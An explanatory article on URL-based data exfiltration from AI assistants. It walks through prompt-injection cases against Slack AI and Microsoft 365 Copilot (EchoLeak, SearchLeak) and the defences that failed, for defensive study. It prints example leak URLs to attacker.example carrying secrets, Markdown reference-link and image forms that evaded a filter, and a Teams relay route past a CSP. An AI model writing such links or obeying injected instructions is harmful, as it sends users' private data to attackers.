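# Checks on links in AI-generated text that prevent hidden data leaks

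## How a link can carry private data out of an AI assistant

Checks on links in AI-generated text decide which links and images an AI assistant may show, load or open. AI assistants such as ChatGPT, Microsoft Copilot and Google Gemini are programs built on large language models. They answer questions and summarise documents, and often have access to the user's email, files or past conversations. The checks are needed because a web address can contain data as well as a location. If an attacker gets the assistant to write an address containing some of the user's private data, opening it sends that data to the attacker. Security researchers call this data exfiltration, which means moving private data to someone who has no right to it.

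The problem is about as old as AI assistants. Security researcher Johann Rehberger reported it to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, and dozens of similar vulnerabilities have turned up since, according to *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a 2026 post on his blog, Embrace The Red.

### What an address sends to the server

Take an invented address of the kind that might appear in an answer about a trip:

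`https://www.lisbon-guide.example/hotels/view?note=passport%20X4419027#map`

Berners-Lee (2005), in *URI Generic Syntax*, the internet standard for addresses, names five parts.

| Part | In the example | What it is for |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | How to connect |
| Authority (here, the domain) | `www.lisbon-guide.example` | Which server receives the request |
| Path | `/hotels/view` | Usually, which page on that server |
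| Query string | `note=passport%20X4419027` | Further data for the server |
| Fragment | `map` | A place within the page |

The `%20` is the standard's way of writing a space. When someone opens the address, the browser cuts off the fragment and keeps it, and sends the rest. There is nothing underhand about a query string in itself. Search engines use them for search terms and shops use them for product numbers. But the owner of the domain decides what to do with the contents, and most servers write them down by default. The manual for Apache, a widely used web server program, gives a sample log entry. On the same pattern, the visit above would leave a line like this:

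`203.0.113.7 - - [05/Dec/2026:09:14:22 +0000] "GET /hotels/view?note=passport%20X4419027 HTTP/1.1" 404 196`

The log line shows the visitor's network address, then the time, then the request with its full path and query string. The 404 means that the page doesn't exist, but the passport number is still in the log, where the attacker can read it at any time. The line omits the domain only because the server's owner already knows it, and the owner can add it to the log.

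Encrypting the connection doesn't prevent this leak. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url*, a reference page from a non-profit body for software security, warns that HTTPS does not solve the problem of sensitive data in query strings. HTTPS hides the request from eavesdroppers along the way, but here the attacker is the one receiving it. The data can leak even if the recipient is honest, because query strings also end up in browser histories and can reach other websites through the header that identifies the page a visitor came from, as MITRE notes in its public catalogue of software weaknesses.

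Microsoft (2025), in an account of its own defences, notes that an attacker can disguise the data by having it encoded in base64 and placed in a subdomain or the path instead of the query string. Base64 is a standard way to rewrite any data as letters, digits and a few symbols. It turns the passport number X4419027 into `WDQ0MTkwMjc=`. A filter looking for passport numbers would miss this string, and a person glancing at the address would take it for one of the meaningless codes common in web addresses.

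### Link text and destination

Most readers never glance at the address, because the assistant's answer doesn't display it. Chat programs generally have the model write in Markdown, a plain-text notation that the program then turns into formatted text. The manual for the document converter Pandoc describes the usual form of a link: the visible words in square brackets, then the address in parentheses. So the model writes

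`[Lisbon hotel guide](https://www.lisbon-guide.example/hotels/view?note=passport%20X4419027)`

and the reader sees only the words "Lisbon hotel guide", underlined or in blue. The visible words are the link text and the address is the destination. Nothing in the notation ties one to the other. The link text could just as well be "source" or even the address of a bank. Markdown also has a reference form, in which the link text carries a label and the address stands elsewhere in the document, so a program that looks for addresses only in parentheses will overlook some. An exclamation mark before the first bracket makes the whole thing an image.

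Web pages have always allowed a link's text to differ from its destination, and phishers have used this to deceive people for decades. In an AI-written answer, however, the misleading text comes from a tool that the reader chose and probably trusts, rather than from a stranger.

### Instructions hidden in what the assistant reads

In these cases, the attacker can write something that the victim's assistant will later read, but has no access to the victim's account and never talks to the assistant.

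That technique is indirect prompt injection, and Microsoft explains it with a web page. A user asks Copilot to summarise the page. The program fetches the text, joins it to the user's request and gives the model the combination as a single input. If the page contains a sentence worded as an instruction, the model may follow it as though the user had typed it. The attacker can print the sentence in white on a white background, or in characters that don't display at all, so the user has no chance to notice it. An email or a shared document works as well as a web page, and a plain text file is enough. (In direct prompt injection, by contrast, the attacker is the person typing to the assistant.)

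*Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) gave the first systematic account and classified the possible attacks. The researchers tried several of them on mock applications and on Bing Chat, then Microsoft's search assistant, which could read whatever page the user had open in the browser. They put instructions in comments in the page's code, which browsers do not show, and then chatted with the assistant as an ordinary user would.

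In one session, the hidden instructions told the model to get the user's real name. It asked friendly questions about the user's plans and work, and learned that the user was a journalist. After the user gave a name, John Smith, the model offered a link to an exclusive website, with a personal access code at the end of the address. The code was roughly the name spelled backwards. Because it came after the `#`, in the fragment, the browser would not have sent it to the server with the request. The attacker would have needed a script on the page to read it, or the user to type it in, as the model suggested. The instructions told the model to be persuasive without raising suspicion but did not specify a method, so the model itself came up with the exclusive website and the code.

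These demonstrations on 2023 models show that the attack is possible, but they don't measure how often it works. Models have become far more capable since, yet the underlying weakness has persisted. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) traces it to the way a model takes in text. The user's request and the stranger's web page end up in one sequence of tokens (the word fragments that models process), and the model cannot reliably rank instructions by where they came from. Telling the model to ignore instructions in documents helps, but developers cannot list every way an instruction might be phrased.

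Microsoft distinguishes between probabilistic and deterministic defences. A probabilistic defence, such as a warning in the model's instructions or a classifier that looks for injected text, makes an attack less likely to succeed. A deterministic defence guarantees that a particular attack fails whatever the model does. In 2025, Microsoft called the deterministic detection of injections an open research problem. Blocking a link is much easier to guarantee, because ordinary code can do it after the model has finished writing. That code can stop the data from leaving even when an undetected injection has manipulated the model.

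### The three conditions for a leak

An injection can steal data only when three conditions hold together, a combination Willison calls the "lethal trifecta". The assistant must have access to private data, take in untrusted content (text that an attacker could have written), and have some way to send information out. If any of the three is missing, the theft fails, though the injection may still do other damage, such as falsifying a summary.

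The last condition is easy to meet. Willison counts a link for the user to click as a way to send data out, so even an assistant that cannot send email or fill in forms can meet it. In August 2024, researchers got Slack's assistant to put an API key (a password for programs) in a link that read "click here to reauthenticate". Willison lists 14 reports of data theft by injection between April 2023 and February 2025, against products from OpenAI, Google, Microsoft, Amazon, Anthropic and others. The vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the way out. They had little alternative, because access to private data and outside text is what makes an assistant useful.

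Summarising an inbox meets the first two conditions almost by definition, because the program puts confidential messages and whatever strangers have sent into the same input. The user doesn't have to do anything careless. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes a January 2026 case in which a user asked the email program Superhuman to summarise recent mail. Following instructions in one untrusted email, the program sent the contents of dozens of other messages, some of them financial, legal and medical, to an attacker's online form. Google DeepMind's security team used the same kind of request in its own testing. Willison's *33 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”* describes the test, in which the user mentions a passport or social security number in an invented conversation, then asks for a summary of the latest email, which the attacker wrote. In that test, the data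 could leak through an email sent by the assistant, but a link would also have worked.

Summaries also help the attacker because readers expect them to contain links, as assistants that search the web normally cite their sources with links in the running text. Greshake and colleagues considered a malicious link placed among these as a suggestion for further reading arguably more dangerous than one that openly pushes the reader to click. Because it looks like the other links, a reader assumes that the assistant copied it from one of the sources. The reader can't easily check this, having asked for a summary to avoid reading the sources.

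### One click or none

With an ordinary link, the data leaves when the user clicks. This one-click leak depends on the link text being tempting or unremarkable enough for someone to follow it.

Images remove the need for a click. To display an image in an answer, the browser requests it from the address the model wrote as soon as the answer appears. Microsoft also describes this route, in which the private data is part of the image's address and the attacker's server receives it without any action by the user. The image can be a single transparent pixel. This kind of request is called an automatic fetch, and a leak that needs no click is called a zero-click leak.

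Other programs also fetch links automatically. Slack, Telegram and similar messaging apps open the links in a message to build a small preview. PromptArmor, a security company, found that when an assistant posts its answers in these apps, a leak that would otherwise require the user to click a link happens without a click. Assistants that browse the web also open links themselves. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes that in both cases the request can happen in the background without the user noticing.

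Zero-click leaks are more serious than leaks that require a click, and vendors have tended to deal with them first. They are also easier to prevent, because a chat program can refuse to load outside images and remain usable. Refusing to show links is less practical, because an assistant that answers questions from the web would be less useful without links to its sources, and its answers would be harder to verify.

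### Filters and the ways around them

The usual defences act on the model's output or on the requests it triggers. A sanitizer is code that removes or disables dangerous links, images or markup before the program displays the text. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks*, Gemini's sanitizer blocks images with outside addresses. An allowlist is a list of the only domains or addresses that a program may contact.

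A Content Security Policy (CSP) is an allowlist, sent by a website to the browser, of the domains its pages may load content from. Even if a malicious image gets past the sanitizer, the browser won't request it from a domain that isn't on the list. In May 2023, after Rehberger's report, Microsoft used a CSP to stop Bing Chat from loading images. But a rule about loading images doesn't cover ordinary links, because clicking one takes the user away from the page instead of loading something into it.

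A list of approved domains is only as safe as the pages and services on those domains. Many sites have a page that forwards visitors to another address given in the query string, as in `https://approved.example/go?to=https://attacker.example/`. If that page forwards to any address it is given, it is an open redirect. A filter that checks only the first domain will allow the request, and the approved site will forward it to the attacker. An open redirect is one kind of relay, a permitted service that passes a request on to a server that isn't permitted. Another kind fetches the second address itself, as an image-resizing or translation service might.

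Sometimes the attacker doesn't need a relay. Superhuman had a content security policy (CSP), but Willison attributes the leak to a rule in it that allowed images from docs.google.com. Google Forms runs on that domain and stores data sent to it in a URL, so the attacker only had to create a form there and read the entries.

### Why a newly composed address is suspect

All of these filters check where an address leads. A filter could also check where the address came from. An attacker who cannot see a secret cannot write an address that contains it, so the assistant has to compose that address after reading the secret. The finished address therefore cannot have been in the attacker's email or web page.

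Software can test for this without interpreting the data. It compares each address in the answer with the addresses in the input and treats any new one as suspect. Google has built such a rule into Gemini. Anthropic applied the same reasoning to the tool its Claude models use to open web pages. Willison noted that when the tool came out in September 2025, Claude could open addresses supplied by the user or returned by earlier searches and page visits, but not addresses it had constructed itself.

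This reasoning has a gap. An attacker can't write an address containing the secret in advance, but can write many addresses and have the assistant choose among them. If the attacker prepares *k* addresses, one visit shows which one the assistant picked, which gives the attacker at most log₂ *k* bits. Embrace The Red describes a version with 36 addresses, for the letters A to Z and the digits 0 to 9, in which each visit reveals one character, or about 5.2 bits. A random 20-character key made of digits and upper- and lower-case letters has 62²⁰ possible values, around 7 × 10³⁵, so no attacker could prepare an address for each and collect the key with one click. But an assistant that opens pages by itself could reveal the key one character at a time in 20 visits. For a yes-or-no secret, such as whether someone has a certain illness, two addresses and one click are enough.

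Ayush Paul showed in July 2026 that this works in practice. Claude's tool could still follow links on pages it had already opened. Paul built a website that claimed to need the user's name for authentication and offered a link for each letter of the alphabet, with further links behind each one. Claude followed the links letter by letter, and the sequence of visits spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. The rule against constructed addresses never applied because the site had supplied every address. Anthropic closed the gap by no longer letting the tool follow links from pages it had fetched. Embrace The Red suggests the milder measure of stopping an assistant from visiting the same full address twice in a session. That would hamper an attacker who uses one fixed address per letter, but not a site like Paul's if it generates new addresses at every step.

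The test can also flag harmless links. Someone who asks for directions home may get a map link with a street address in the query string. The user wanted this link, but the assistant composed it and it contains private data, so comparing it with the input cannot distinguish it from a link that steals data. The domain gives some indication, and so does the rest of the URL if the program lets the user see it.

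## Slack AI, 2024: an API key behind the words "click here to reauthenticate"

Slack is a workplace messaging service. A company's staff share a workspace and talk in channels, some open to everyone in it and some private. Slack's assistant, Slack AI, answered questions about the messages in these channels. In August 2024, PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* showed how a member of a workspace could use one public message to steal an API key from a private channel.

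Slack built the assistant under a privacy rule, described on its engineering blog, that the model receives only data the user can already see and that only this user sees the answer. The attack didn't break this rule, because the victim was allowed to read both the key and the attacker's message, and nobody else saw the answer. But the rule doesn't cover what happens when the user clicks a link in that answer.

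### How the key got into the link

The victim in the demonstration kept an API key for a service called EldritchNexus in a private channel with no other members. The attacker created a public channel, added nobody else and posted a message there. Any member of a Slack workspace can search public channels they haven't joined, so Slack AI could use the attacker's message when it answered the victim.

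The message began with the name of the key, which presumably helped a search for the key to find it. It then told the model to answer with an error message and a link, and to replace a placeholder word in the link's address with the real key. With an invented domain, the address in the attacker's message looked like this:

`https://attacker.example/?secret=PLACEHOLDER`

The victim then asked Slack AI for the EldritchNexus key. Slack AI worked by retrieval-augmented generation: the program searches for relevant messages and gives them to the model along with the question. The search returned both the victim's own message and the attacker's, and the model followed the instruction in the second. It wrote an address of this form (the key here is invented too):

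`https://attacker.example/?secret=EN-7f3k-29qd`

The victim saw only an error message and a link labeled "click here to reauthenticate". Clicking it would send the API key to the attacker's server, where the attacker could read it in the log.

The attacker never needed to see the key, because the model filled it in. PromptArmor thought the attacker might not even need to name a particular key, since the victim's question also brought up other messages about API keys, but it didn't demonstrate this. In *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, Willison (2024) treats the key as only an illustration and sees a bigger risk in attackers having many opportunities to plant such messages and being able to target all kinds of private information. PromptArmor showed that the attack could work but gave no success rate.

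The attacker needed an account in the victim's workspace, which limited the attack to colleagues and anyone who had taken over a colleague's account. PromptArmor pointed out, though, that insiders had already leaked data from Slack at companies including Disney and Uber. Slack may also have removed this requirement on August 14, 2024, when Slack AI began to use uploaded files as well as messages. An outsider could hide instructions in white text in a PDF and wait for an employee to upload it. PromptArmor had finished testing before the change and did not try this route, but called it highly likely to work.

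### Why the victim had little to notice

People often have to log in to office software again, so the message was unremarkable. The victim also had a reason to click, because they had asked for a key and logging in again looked like the way to get it.

Slack AI's answers carried numbered citations to their source messages, but the only citation in this answer pointed to the victim's own private channel. A victim who followed it would have found the genuine key in a message they had written themselves, and would probably have trusted the answer more. The answer did not cite the attacker's message, so nothing in it led back to the attacker, which would also hamper an investigation.

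PromptArmor considered this a separate fault, because a correct answer cites every message that contributed to it. Ordinary code can prevent the fault by listing every message it gave to the model, whatever the model writes. The list would include some irrelevant messages, but it would also include the attacker's.

Ordinary search didn't help either, because the attacker's message wasn't on the first page of results and the victim might have had to scroll through several pages to find it. The attacker's channel showed up only for people who searched for it, and large workspaces have too many public channels for anyone to keep track of. SC Media's *Slack patches Slack AI issue that could have allowed insider phishing* notes that posting in public still carries some risk of discovery, but someone has to come across the channel first.

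The only visible sign was the link's address, which appeared when the victim hovered over the link. It showed an unfamiliar domain followed by the key in plain text. This helps only people who check addresses before they click.

### A phishing link with no secret in it

In PromptArmor's second demonstration, a user asked Slack AI to summarise the day's messages from a manager. The attacker had again posted in a public channel with no other members, this time naming the manager and telling the model to include a login link. Slack AI's answer contained the link, with the same "click here to reauthenticate" text. An attacker could name anyone in such a message. To target an executive, for example, they could name one of the executive's close colleagues.

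This time, the citation pointed to the attacker's channel. PromptArmor concluded that Slack AI's citations were fairly random. An answer that cited no suspicious source could therefore still be unsafe.

A reader would see the same words in both demonstrations, but the links work differently. The first is a leaking link, with the secret in its address, so the theft is complete once the browser requests the page, even if the page is blank. The second is a phishing link. Its address contains nothing private, and the attacker gets a password only if the victim types it into the attacker's page. Someone who never enters a password on an unfamiliar site would still lose the key by clicking the first link.

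Software that looks for private data in addresses would not flag the phishing link, because its address contains none. The attacker can also write the whole address in advance, so the model only has to copy it.

### The dispute and the patch

PromptArmor reported the problem to Slack on August 14, 2024. Slack asked for more information the next day, and PromptArmor sent videos and screenshots. It also said it planned to publish because of the severity of the problem and the new file feature. After more questions and answers on August 16, Slack replied on August 19 that it found the evidence insufficient. It said the information in the first video came from a public channel, and that any member can search public channels, which "is intended behavior".

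PromptArmor published its findings the next day, six days after its first report, saying users needed to know so they could change their settings. Willison thought Slack's reply showed that the company did not yet understand the nature or severity of the problem. But PromptArmor praised Slack's security team for responding quickly and said the whole industry still misunderstood prompt injection.

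Slack was right that public messages are meant to be searchable. If the citation in the video did point to a public channel, Slack's reviewers also had some reason to think that no private data was involved. In PromptArmor's published account, however, the key was in a private channel and the citation pointed to that channel. Either way, the intended search behaviour explains how the attacker's message reached the model, but not why the model should put a user's key into a link to an outside website.

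Slack soon acted on the report, announcing on August 21 that it had deployed a patch the day before (Slack, 2024). It said that "under very limited and specific circumstances", someone with an account in the workspace could phish other users for certain data. It also said it had no evidence "at this time" of unauthorized access to customer data. A Salesforce spokesperson gave SC Media almost the same statement but did not answer its question about instructions hidden in files.

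The absence of evidence is mildly reassuring at best, because a click sends the data straight from the victim's browser to the attacker's server, and Slack's servers wouldn't necessarily have a record of it. According to Slack's engineering blog, the company also did not store Slack AI's search answers on disk, which would have left few past answers to inspect. Slack could still have searched public channels for messages like the attacker's.

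In a separate statement, quoted in ITPro's *Hackers could dupe Slack's AI features to expose private channel messages*, Slack described an attacker who tricks a colleague "into sharing sensitive data by crafting a phishing link". That description fits the second demonstration better than the first, where the model had already put the key in the link's address and the victim typed nothing into the attacker's site. The difference matters for judging the patch because a fix for phishing links won't necessarily stop links that leak data. Slack didn't explain whether it had changed the search, the model's instructions or the treatment of links.

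The demonstrations predate the patch that Slack deployed in August 2024. *SecAlign* (2024), a paper on training models to resist prompt injection, still described the attack that October as working in the current Slack AI.

### How Slack handles links now

Slack's current assistant is Slackbot, which the company rebuilt as an AI agent in early 2026 and protects with the Slack AI Guardrails. Slack's guide to the guardrails lists "URL filtering to prevent phishing attacks", along with checks on the format of the model's output and measures to reduce the risk of prompt injection. If an answer fails a check, Slack may alter or block it. An administrator can switch off the content safety filters, which by default try to block prompt attacks among other things, but the URL filtering stays on. Slack had URL filtering by 2025, when *Securing the Agentic Enterprise* (2025) mentioned it.

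Slack doesn't explain in these descriptions how the filter judges an address. Many phishing filters check addresses against lists of known malicious sites. Such a filter could miss a domain an attacker registered the day before, whatever the query string contained. A filter that also compared addresses with the retrieved messages would have a much better chance of stopping the 2024 attack. Slack's filter may do this, but describing it as phishing protection is no evidence that it does.

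Citations seem to have improved. In Slack's own account, *How We Rebuilt Slackbot*, Seaman (2026) writes that the assistant links to its sources and gives clear citations. The company's security page says only that answers "may include citations". Users still can't assume that the citations cover everything the model read.

Attackers now have more places to put their text. In 2024, Slack presented it as an advantage that Slack AI drew on a company's own knowledge and not the public internet. Slackbot can now search the web if administrators allow it, according to Slack's user guide. It can also read files and use connected outside services for longer research tasks. Any web page it reads could contain instructions from someone with no account in the workspace, so Slack can no longer assume an attacker is an insider.

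Similar leaks still occur in other workplace assistants. PromptArmor's *Atlassian Rovo Exfiltrates Data, Bypassing Controls* describes an attack in which Atlassian's assistant leaked project tickets and internal documents to the attacker's logs without anyone clicking a link.

### What simple defences would have done

PromptArmor published enough detail to work out how some simple defences would have fared against its two demonstrations.

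The bluntest check is to remove every link that the model writes. The program would keep the words "click here to reauthenticate" as plain text and delete the address, which would stop both attacks. It has to delete the address completely, because many chat programs turn a bare address back into a link, and some also open it to build a preview. But people often ask a workplace assistant where to find a document, and the best answer is a link. The program could still provide citations, because it can build links to Slack messages from its own record of the search without letting the model write any part of the address.

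A gentler measure is to show the domain beside the link text. In both demonstrations, the user would have seen "click here to reauthenticate" next to aiexecutiveorder.com, which has no apparent connection to Slack or EldritchNexus. That is a good warning for anyone who reads it, but PromptArmor did not try to disguise the domain, and a real attacker could register one that resembled the service's name. Showing only the domain also hides the strongest evidence, the key in the query string. Showing the full address would reveal the key, unless the attacker had told the model to encode it first.

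The program could instead compare each address in the answer with the addresses in the retrieved messages, and block those that don't match. The result depends on how much of the address it compares:

| Part compared | Leaking link | Phishing link |
|---|---|---|
| Domain only | Passes | Passes |
| Everything before the question mark | Passes | Passes |
| Full address | Blocked | Passes |

Domain matching does not catch the leaking link because the attacker's message supplied the domain. A check that ignores the query string also fails, because the same message supplied everything in the address except the key. Exact matching catches the link because the retrieved messages contained the address only with a placeholder in place of the key. If the model had copied that address unchanged, the link would have passed the check, but a click would have sent the attacker only the placeholder.

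Unlike a search for secrets, exact matching would catch the link even if the model had encoded the key. The program can safely ignore differences that don't affect the request, such as capital letters in the domain, as long as it compares the whole path and query string.

Exact matching doesn't stop the phishing link, because its full address can already be in the attacker's message. To catch it, the program has to check who wrote that message. The user had asked for a summary of the manager's messages, and the link came from someone else's. If the program recorded the author of each retrieved message along with its addresses, it could drop any link that the manager hadn't posted. It could also exclude the attacker's message from the search. Seaman reports that Slackbot can now filter searches by sender. This would have kept the message out of the summary if Slackbot had applied the filter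 and the attacker wasn't using the manager's account.

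## Microsoft 365 Copilot, 2025 and 2026: link filters and how they failed

Microsoft 365 Copilot is Microsoft's assistant for Word, Outlook, Teams and other office programs. By early 2025 it had several protections against links that leak data. A classifier looked for injected instructions in incoming text, a filter removed outside links from answers, and a content security policy (CSP) limited where images could come from. Between June 2025 and December 2026, security researchers published three sets of attacks, called EchoLeak, SearchLeak and ReLeak, that got past these protections. Microsoft fixed the flaws each time before the details came out, and nobody has reported a real attack that used them.

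### EchoLeak: an outsider's email in an employee's answer

Copilot answers questions by retrieval, much as Slack AI did. It searches the user's mailbox, files, internal websites and chat history. Only employees can use a company's Copilot, but anyone can email an employee. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explained that an attacker needed no other access to exploit EchoLeak. Ravia heads Cato AI Labs, which found the vulnerability under its earlier name, Aim Labs.

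EchoLeak counts as a zero-click attack, but the victim still had to ask Copilot something, and Copilot had to retrieve the attacker's email from the mailbox. Search systems of this kind often represent each piece of text as a point in a space where texts on similar subjects lie close together, then retrieve the pieces nearest to the question. A short email takes up one point, so few questions will retrieve it. Aim Labs therefore wrote a long email that the system would split into pieces, each with a heading on something employees often ask about, such as leave of absence, and the same instructions underneath. The team didn't know in detail how Copilot's search worked and published no retrieval rate, but in its demonstration Copilot retrieved the email for questions on various topics.

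Microsoft's classifier was supposed to keep the instructions from reaching the model. Aim Labs got past it by writing the email as if to the human recipient and never mentioning Copilot or AI. Office mail often contains requests to look something up and send it on, so a classifier has little to distinguish an attack from ordinary mail, and Ravia considers such emails inherently difficult to detect. The email also asked the "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot left it out of its references. Slack AI's citations had been unreliable even without such a request.

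### The link form that the filter missed

Once the model had read the email, it would write a link containing the most sensitive information it could find in the conversation and the retrieved documents. Copilot's filter removed outside links from answers before the user could click them, but only if the model wrote them in the common form. The table shows the forms Aim Labs tried, with an invented domain.

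| Form | What the model writes | Removed? |
|---|---|---|
| Inline link | `[report](https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET)` | Yes |
| Reference link | `[report][1]`, and on another line `[1]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET` | No |
| Reference link with an empty label | `[report][]`, and on another line `[report]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET` | No |
| Reference link with no label | `[report]`, and on another line `[report]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET` | No |
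| Inline image | `![chart](https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET)` | Yes |
| Reference image | `![chart][1]`, and on another line `[1]: https://attacker.example/?d=SECRET` | No |

All four link forms look identical on the screen. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Willison, 2025), a blog post named after Ravia's, credits Microsoft with showing inline links only if they led to approved internal pages. The rule was right, but the company forgot to apply it to the less common notation.

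The underlying fault was that the filter and the display program used different rules to identify links in the same text. To find a reference link, a program has to collect the addresses from the whole answer and match them to their labels. The matching has its own rules, such as ignoring capitalization in labels, and a filter that gets any of them wrong will let some links through.

Adding the missing forms to the filter closes this gap, but the filter and the display program can still interpret the text differently. The filter has to parse the text exactly as the display program does, and the surest way to do that is to parse it only once. The program turns the answer into a structured list of paragraphs, links and images, checks the destination of every link and image, deletes those that fail, and builds the display from what remains, so every link the reader sees has been checked. If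 the program turns the cleaned list back into Markdown for another program to parse, the same kind of disagreement can return. Google also uses a parser in Gemini's sanitizer.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study based on published material, mentions that Microsoft later began to strip reference links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it. This is worth doing, but the model's answer still needs a filter, because an attacker can describe the link in ordinary prose and have the model write the Markdown.

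### How a permitted domain defeated the CSP

A reference link still needed a click, so Aim Labs next tried reference images, which the browser loads automatically. At this point the CSP stopped the attack.

With invented domains, the part of a CSP that governs images could look like this:

`Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://static.office.example https://*.teams.example`

The first entry permits a single domain, and the asterisk in the second permits every subdomain of teams.example. An entry can also name a path, which narrows it to one folder or file on the server. But an entry can't restrict the query string, so the browser will send any data placed there to a permitted address.

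The list that Ravia published for Copilot has 29 different entries, 11 of them with an asterisk. Most of the 29 belong to Microsoft's own services, including SharePoint, Teams and Bing. An attacker can't run a server at most of these domains, but doesn't need to if one of them offers a relay.

Aim Labs tried SharePoint first. Any organisation can have a site under sharepoint.com, including an attacker, and SharePoint had a function that fetched content from an outside address in order to embed it. When the browser asked SharePoint for the "image", SharePoint's server asked the attacker's server for an address with the secret in it. This worked only if the victim had signed in to SharePoint and accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. The team then found a Teams service that did the same for anyone. In outline, the image's address looked like this:

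`https://gateway.teams.example/fetch?url=https://attacker.example/SECRET`

The browser allowed the request because it went to a Teams domain. The Teams server then fetched the second address, and the secret appeared in the attacker's log.

Willison calls the Teams address an open redirect, but Ravia describes a server that makes the outside request itself. A redirect would have failed, because when a permitted site redirects the browser, the browser checks the new domain against the policy too. The browser cannot apply the policy to requests that a server sends on its behalf, whether that server belongs to Microsoft or another company.

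Reddy and Gujral recommend a CSP that lists only the company's own domains, without asterisks, and an internal proxy for any other permitted images. Listing only its own domains would not have protected Microsoft in this case, because the relay was on one of them. Adding a path to the Teams entry would have helped if Microsoft could limit the entry to a folder containing only images. An approved domain can also change hands, as happened with Salesforce Agentforce, or host a proxy, as happened with GitHub Copilot Chat.

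Reddy and Gujral also suggest a signed proxy. The company's server attaches a code that only it can compute to each image address it has approved, and the proxy refuses any address without a valid code. The model can't forge the code, even if an injection has misled it. But the server needs a reason to approve an address beyond the model having written it, or it will sign the attacker's addresses too. Reddy and Gujral rate eight defences in a table, based on reasoning rather than experiments. They mark the signed proxy, a strict CSP, a list of allowed addresses and human approval as able to stop a zero-click leak, and the other four as unable to.

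### Five months to a fix

Aim Labs reported EchoLeak in January 2025, and Microsoft took five months to deal with it. Adir Gruss, a co-founder of Aim Security, called this unusually long in an interview for Goldman (2025), *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*. According to Gruss, Microsoft attempted a fix in April but found further problems in May. The flaw was of a new kind, and finding the right teams inside Microsoft and explaining it to them took time. The fix ran on Microsoft's servers, so customers had nothing to install. The official record, INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), lists the flaw's severity as 9.3 out of 10.

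Microsoft said that no customers were affected. This is somewhat more credible than Slack's similar statement because the image version of EchoLeak sent data through a Teams server, where Microsoft could look for suspicious requests. In the Slack attack, the data went straight from the victim's browser to the attacker. How much more credible Microsoft's statement is depends on how long the company kept the server's logs and how closely it searched them.

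Ravia proposed the term "LLM scope violation" for cases where untrusted text gets the model to use private data without the user's consent. Ravia argued that precise names lead to precise defences. For example, after programmers identified the stack overflow as a distinct type of memory error, they invented a specific protection against it. Willison saw nothing new in the pattern and no need for the term, since the model still can't take account of where each piece of text came from. Ravia's observation still suggests that software could look for emails from outside the company that refer to "the most sensitive" information elsewhere in a conversation, since such emails have little legitimate reason to do so.

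### SearchLeak: a filter that ran too late

In June 2026, a year after EchoLeak, Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) described an attack on Copilot Enterprise Search, the part of Copilot that finds a company's emails, meetings and files. This time the instructions came in a link. The search page's web address can include a query, so a link can open the page with a search already filled in. Copilot treated this text as instructions as well as search terms. An attacker could therefore send someone a link to a genuine Microsoft page with instructions in the query, and Copilot would follow them after one click.

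The link that the victim clicked contained the attacker's instructions, and the private data leaked through an image in the answer. Because the link's domain was Microsoft's, it looked safe to the victim and to software that blocks known phishing sites. The full address was more suspicious because it contained a long, encoded query. Varonis advises users to be wary of such links even when they lead to Microsoft.

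The same researcher, Dolev Taler, had already used this technique against the personal version of Copilot in an attack called Reprompt, according to The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox*. Taler reported Reprompt in August 2025 and Microsoft patched it in January 2026, but the enterprise search page still accepted instructions in the same way.

In the demonstration, Copilot looked up an email and put its subject line in the address of an image. The attacker's log then showed a request for `/Your_Security_Code_847291/img.png`. Even a leak this short can be harmful, because many services put login codes in subject lines, and a code that is still valid can be enough to get into another account.

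Microsoft had a protection against images in answers. It wrapped the model's output in a code block, which makes a browser display markup as plain text. This works, but Copilot did it only when the answer was complete. Like most chat programs, Copilot streams its answers, which means that it shows the words as the model produces them. Varonis gives the order of events:

1. Partway through the answer, the model writes an image tag.
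2. The browser adds the unfinished answer to the page, treats the tag as an image and requests it.
3. The model finishes writing.
4. Copilot wraps the answer in a code block, and the image turns into harmless text.

By the fourth step, the request had already been sent. Programmers call this a race condition, because the result depends on which of two events happens first. It is easy to miss in testing, because a tester who looks only at the finished answer will see a code block and conclude that the protection works.

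### Filtering an answer while it streams

Varonis recommends sanitizing at the moment of display instead of afterwards. This is harder with Markdown because a link can arrive in pieces. A program that has received only `[report](https://www.exam` can't yet tell where the link goes. It can hold back everything from the opening bracket until the closing parenthesis arrives, then check the complete address.

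Reference links take longer to check, since the label may come in the first paragraph and the address in the last line. The program can show the label as ordinary text and turn it into a link once the address has arrived and passed the check. It can also show an empty box in place of an image until the check is done, and display HTML tags as plain text from the start. Some links appear a moment late, which seems a minor drawback. SearchLeak was possible because Copilot instead treated the markup as live until the filter disabled it.

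The attack still had to get past the CSP, which blocked images from unknown domains but allowed requests to Bing. Bing's image search lets a user submit the address of a picture, which Bing's servers then fetch and analyse. The browser sent a request to Bing, and Bing fetched an address on the attacker's server with the stolen subject line in its path. This type of flaw, in which an attacker gets someone else's server to send a request, is called server-side request forgery and is well over a decade old.

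Bing was already on the list that Ravia published in June 2025. EchoLeak had shown that data can leak through a listed domain if that domain fetches URLs for other people, and Bing's well-known search by image feature does this. Microsoft either didn't check the other domains on its list for the same problem, or did and missed Bing. Varonis now recommends that everyone who maintains a CSP check for it.

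### Why the severity ratings for SearchLeak differ

Microsoft's advisory, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), rates SearchLeak "Critical" on the company's own scale but gives it 6.5 out of 10, or "medium", on the standard Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS). The US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) scores it 7.5, or "high".

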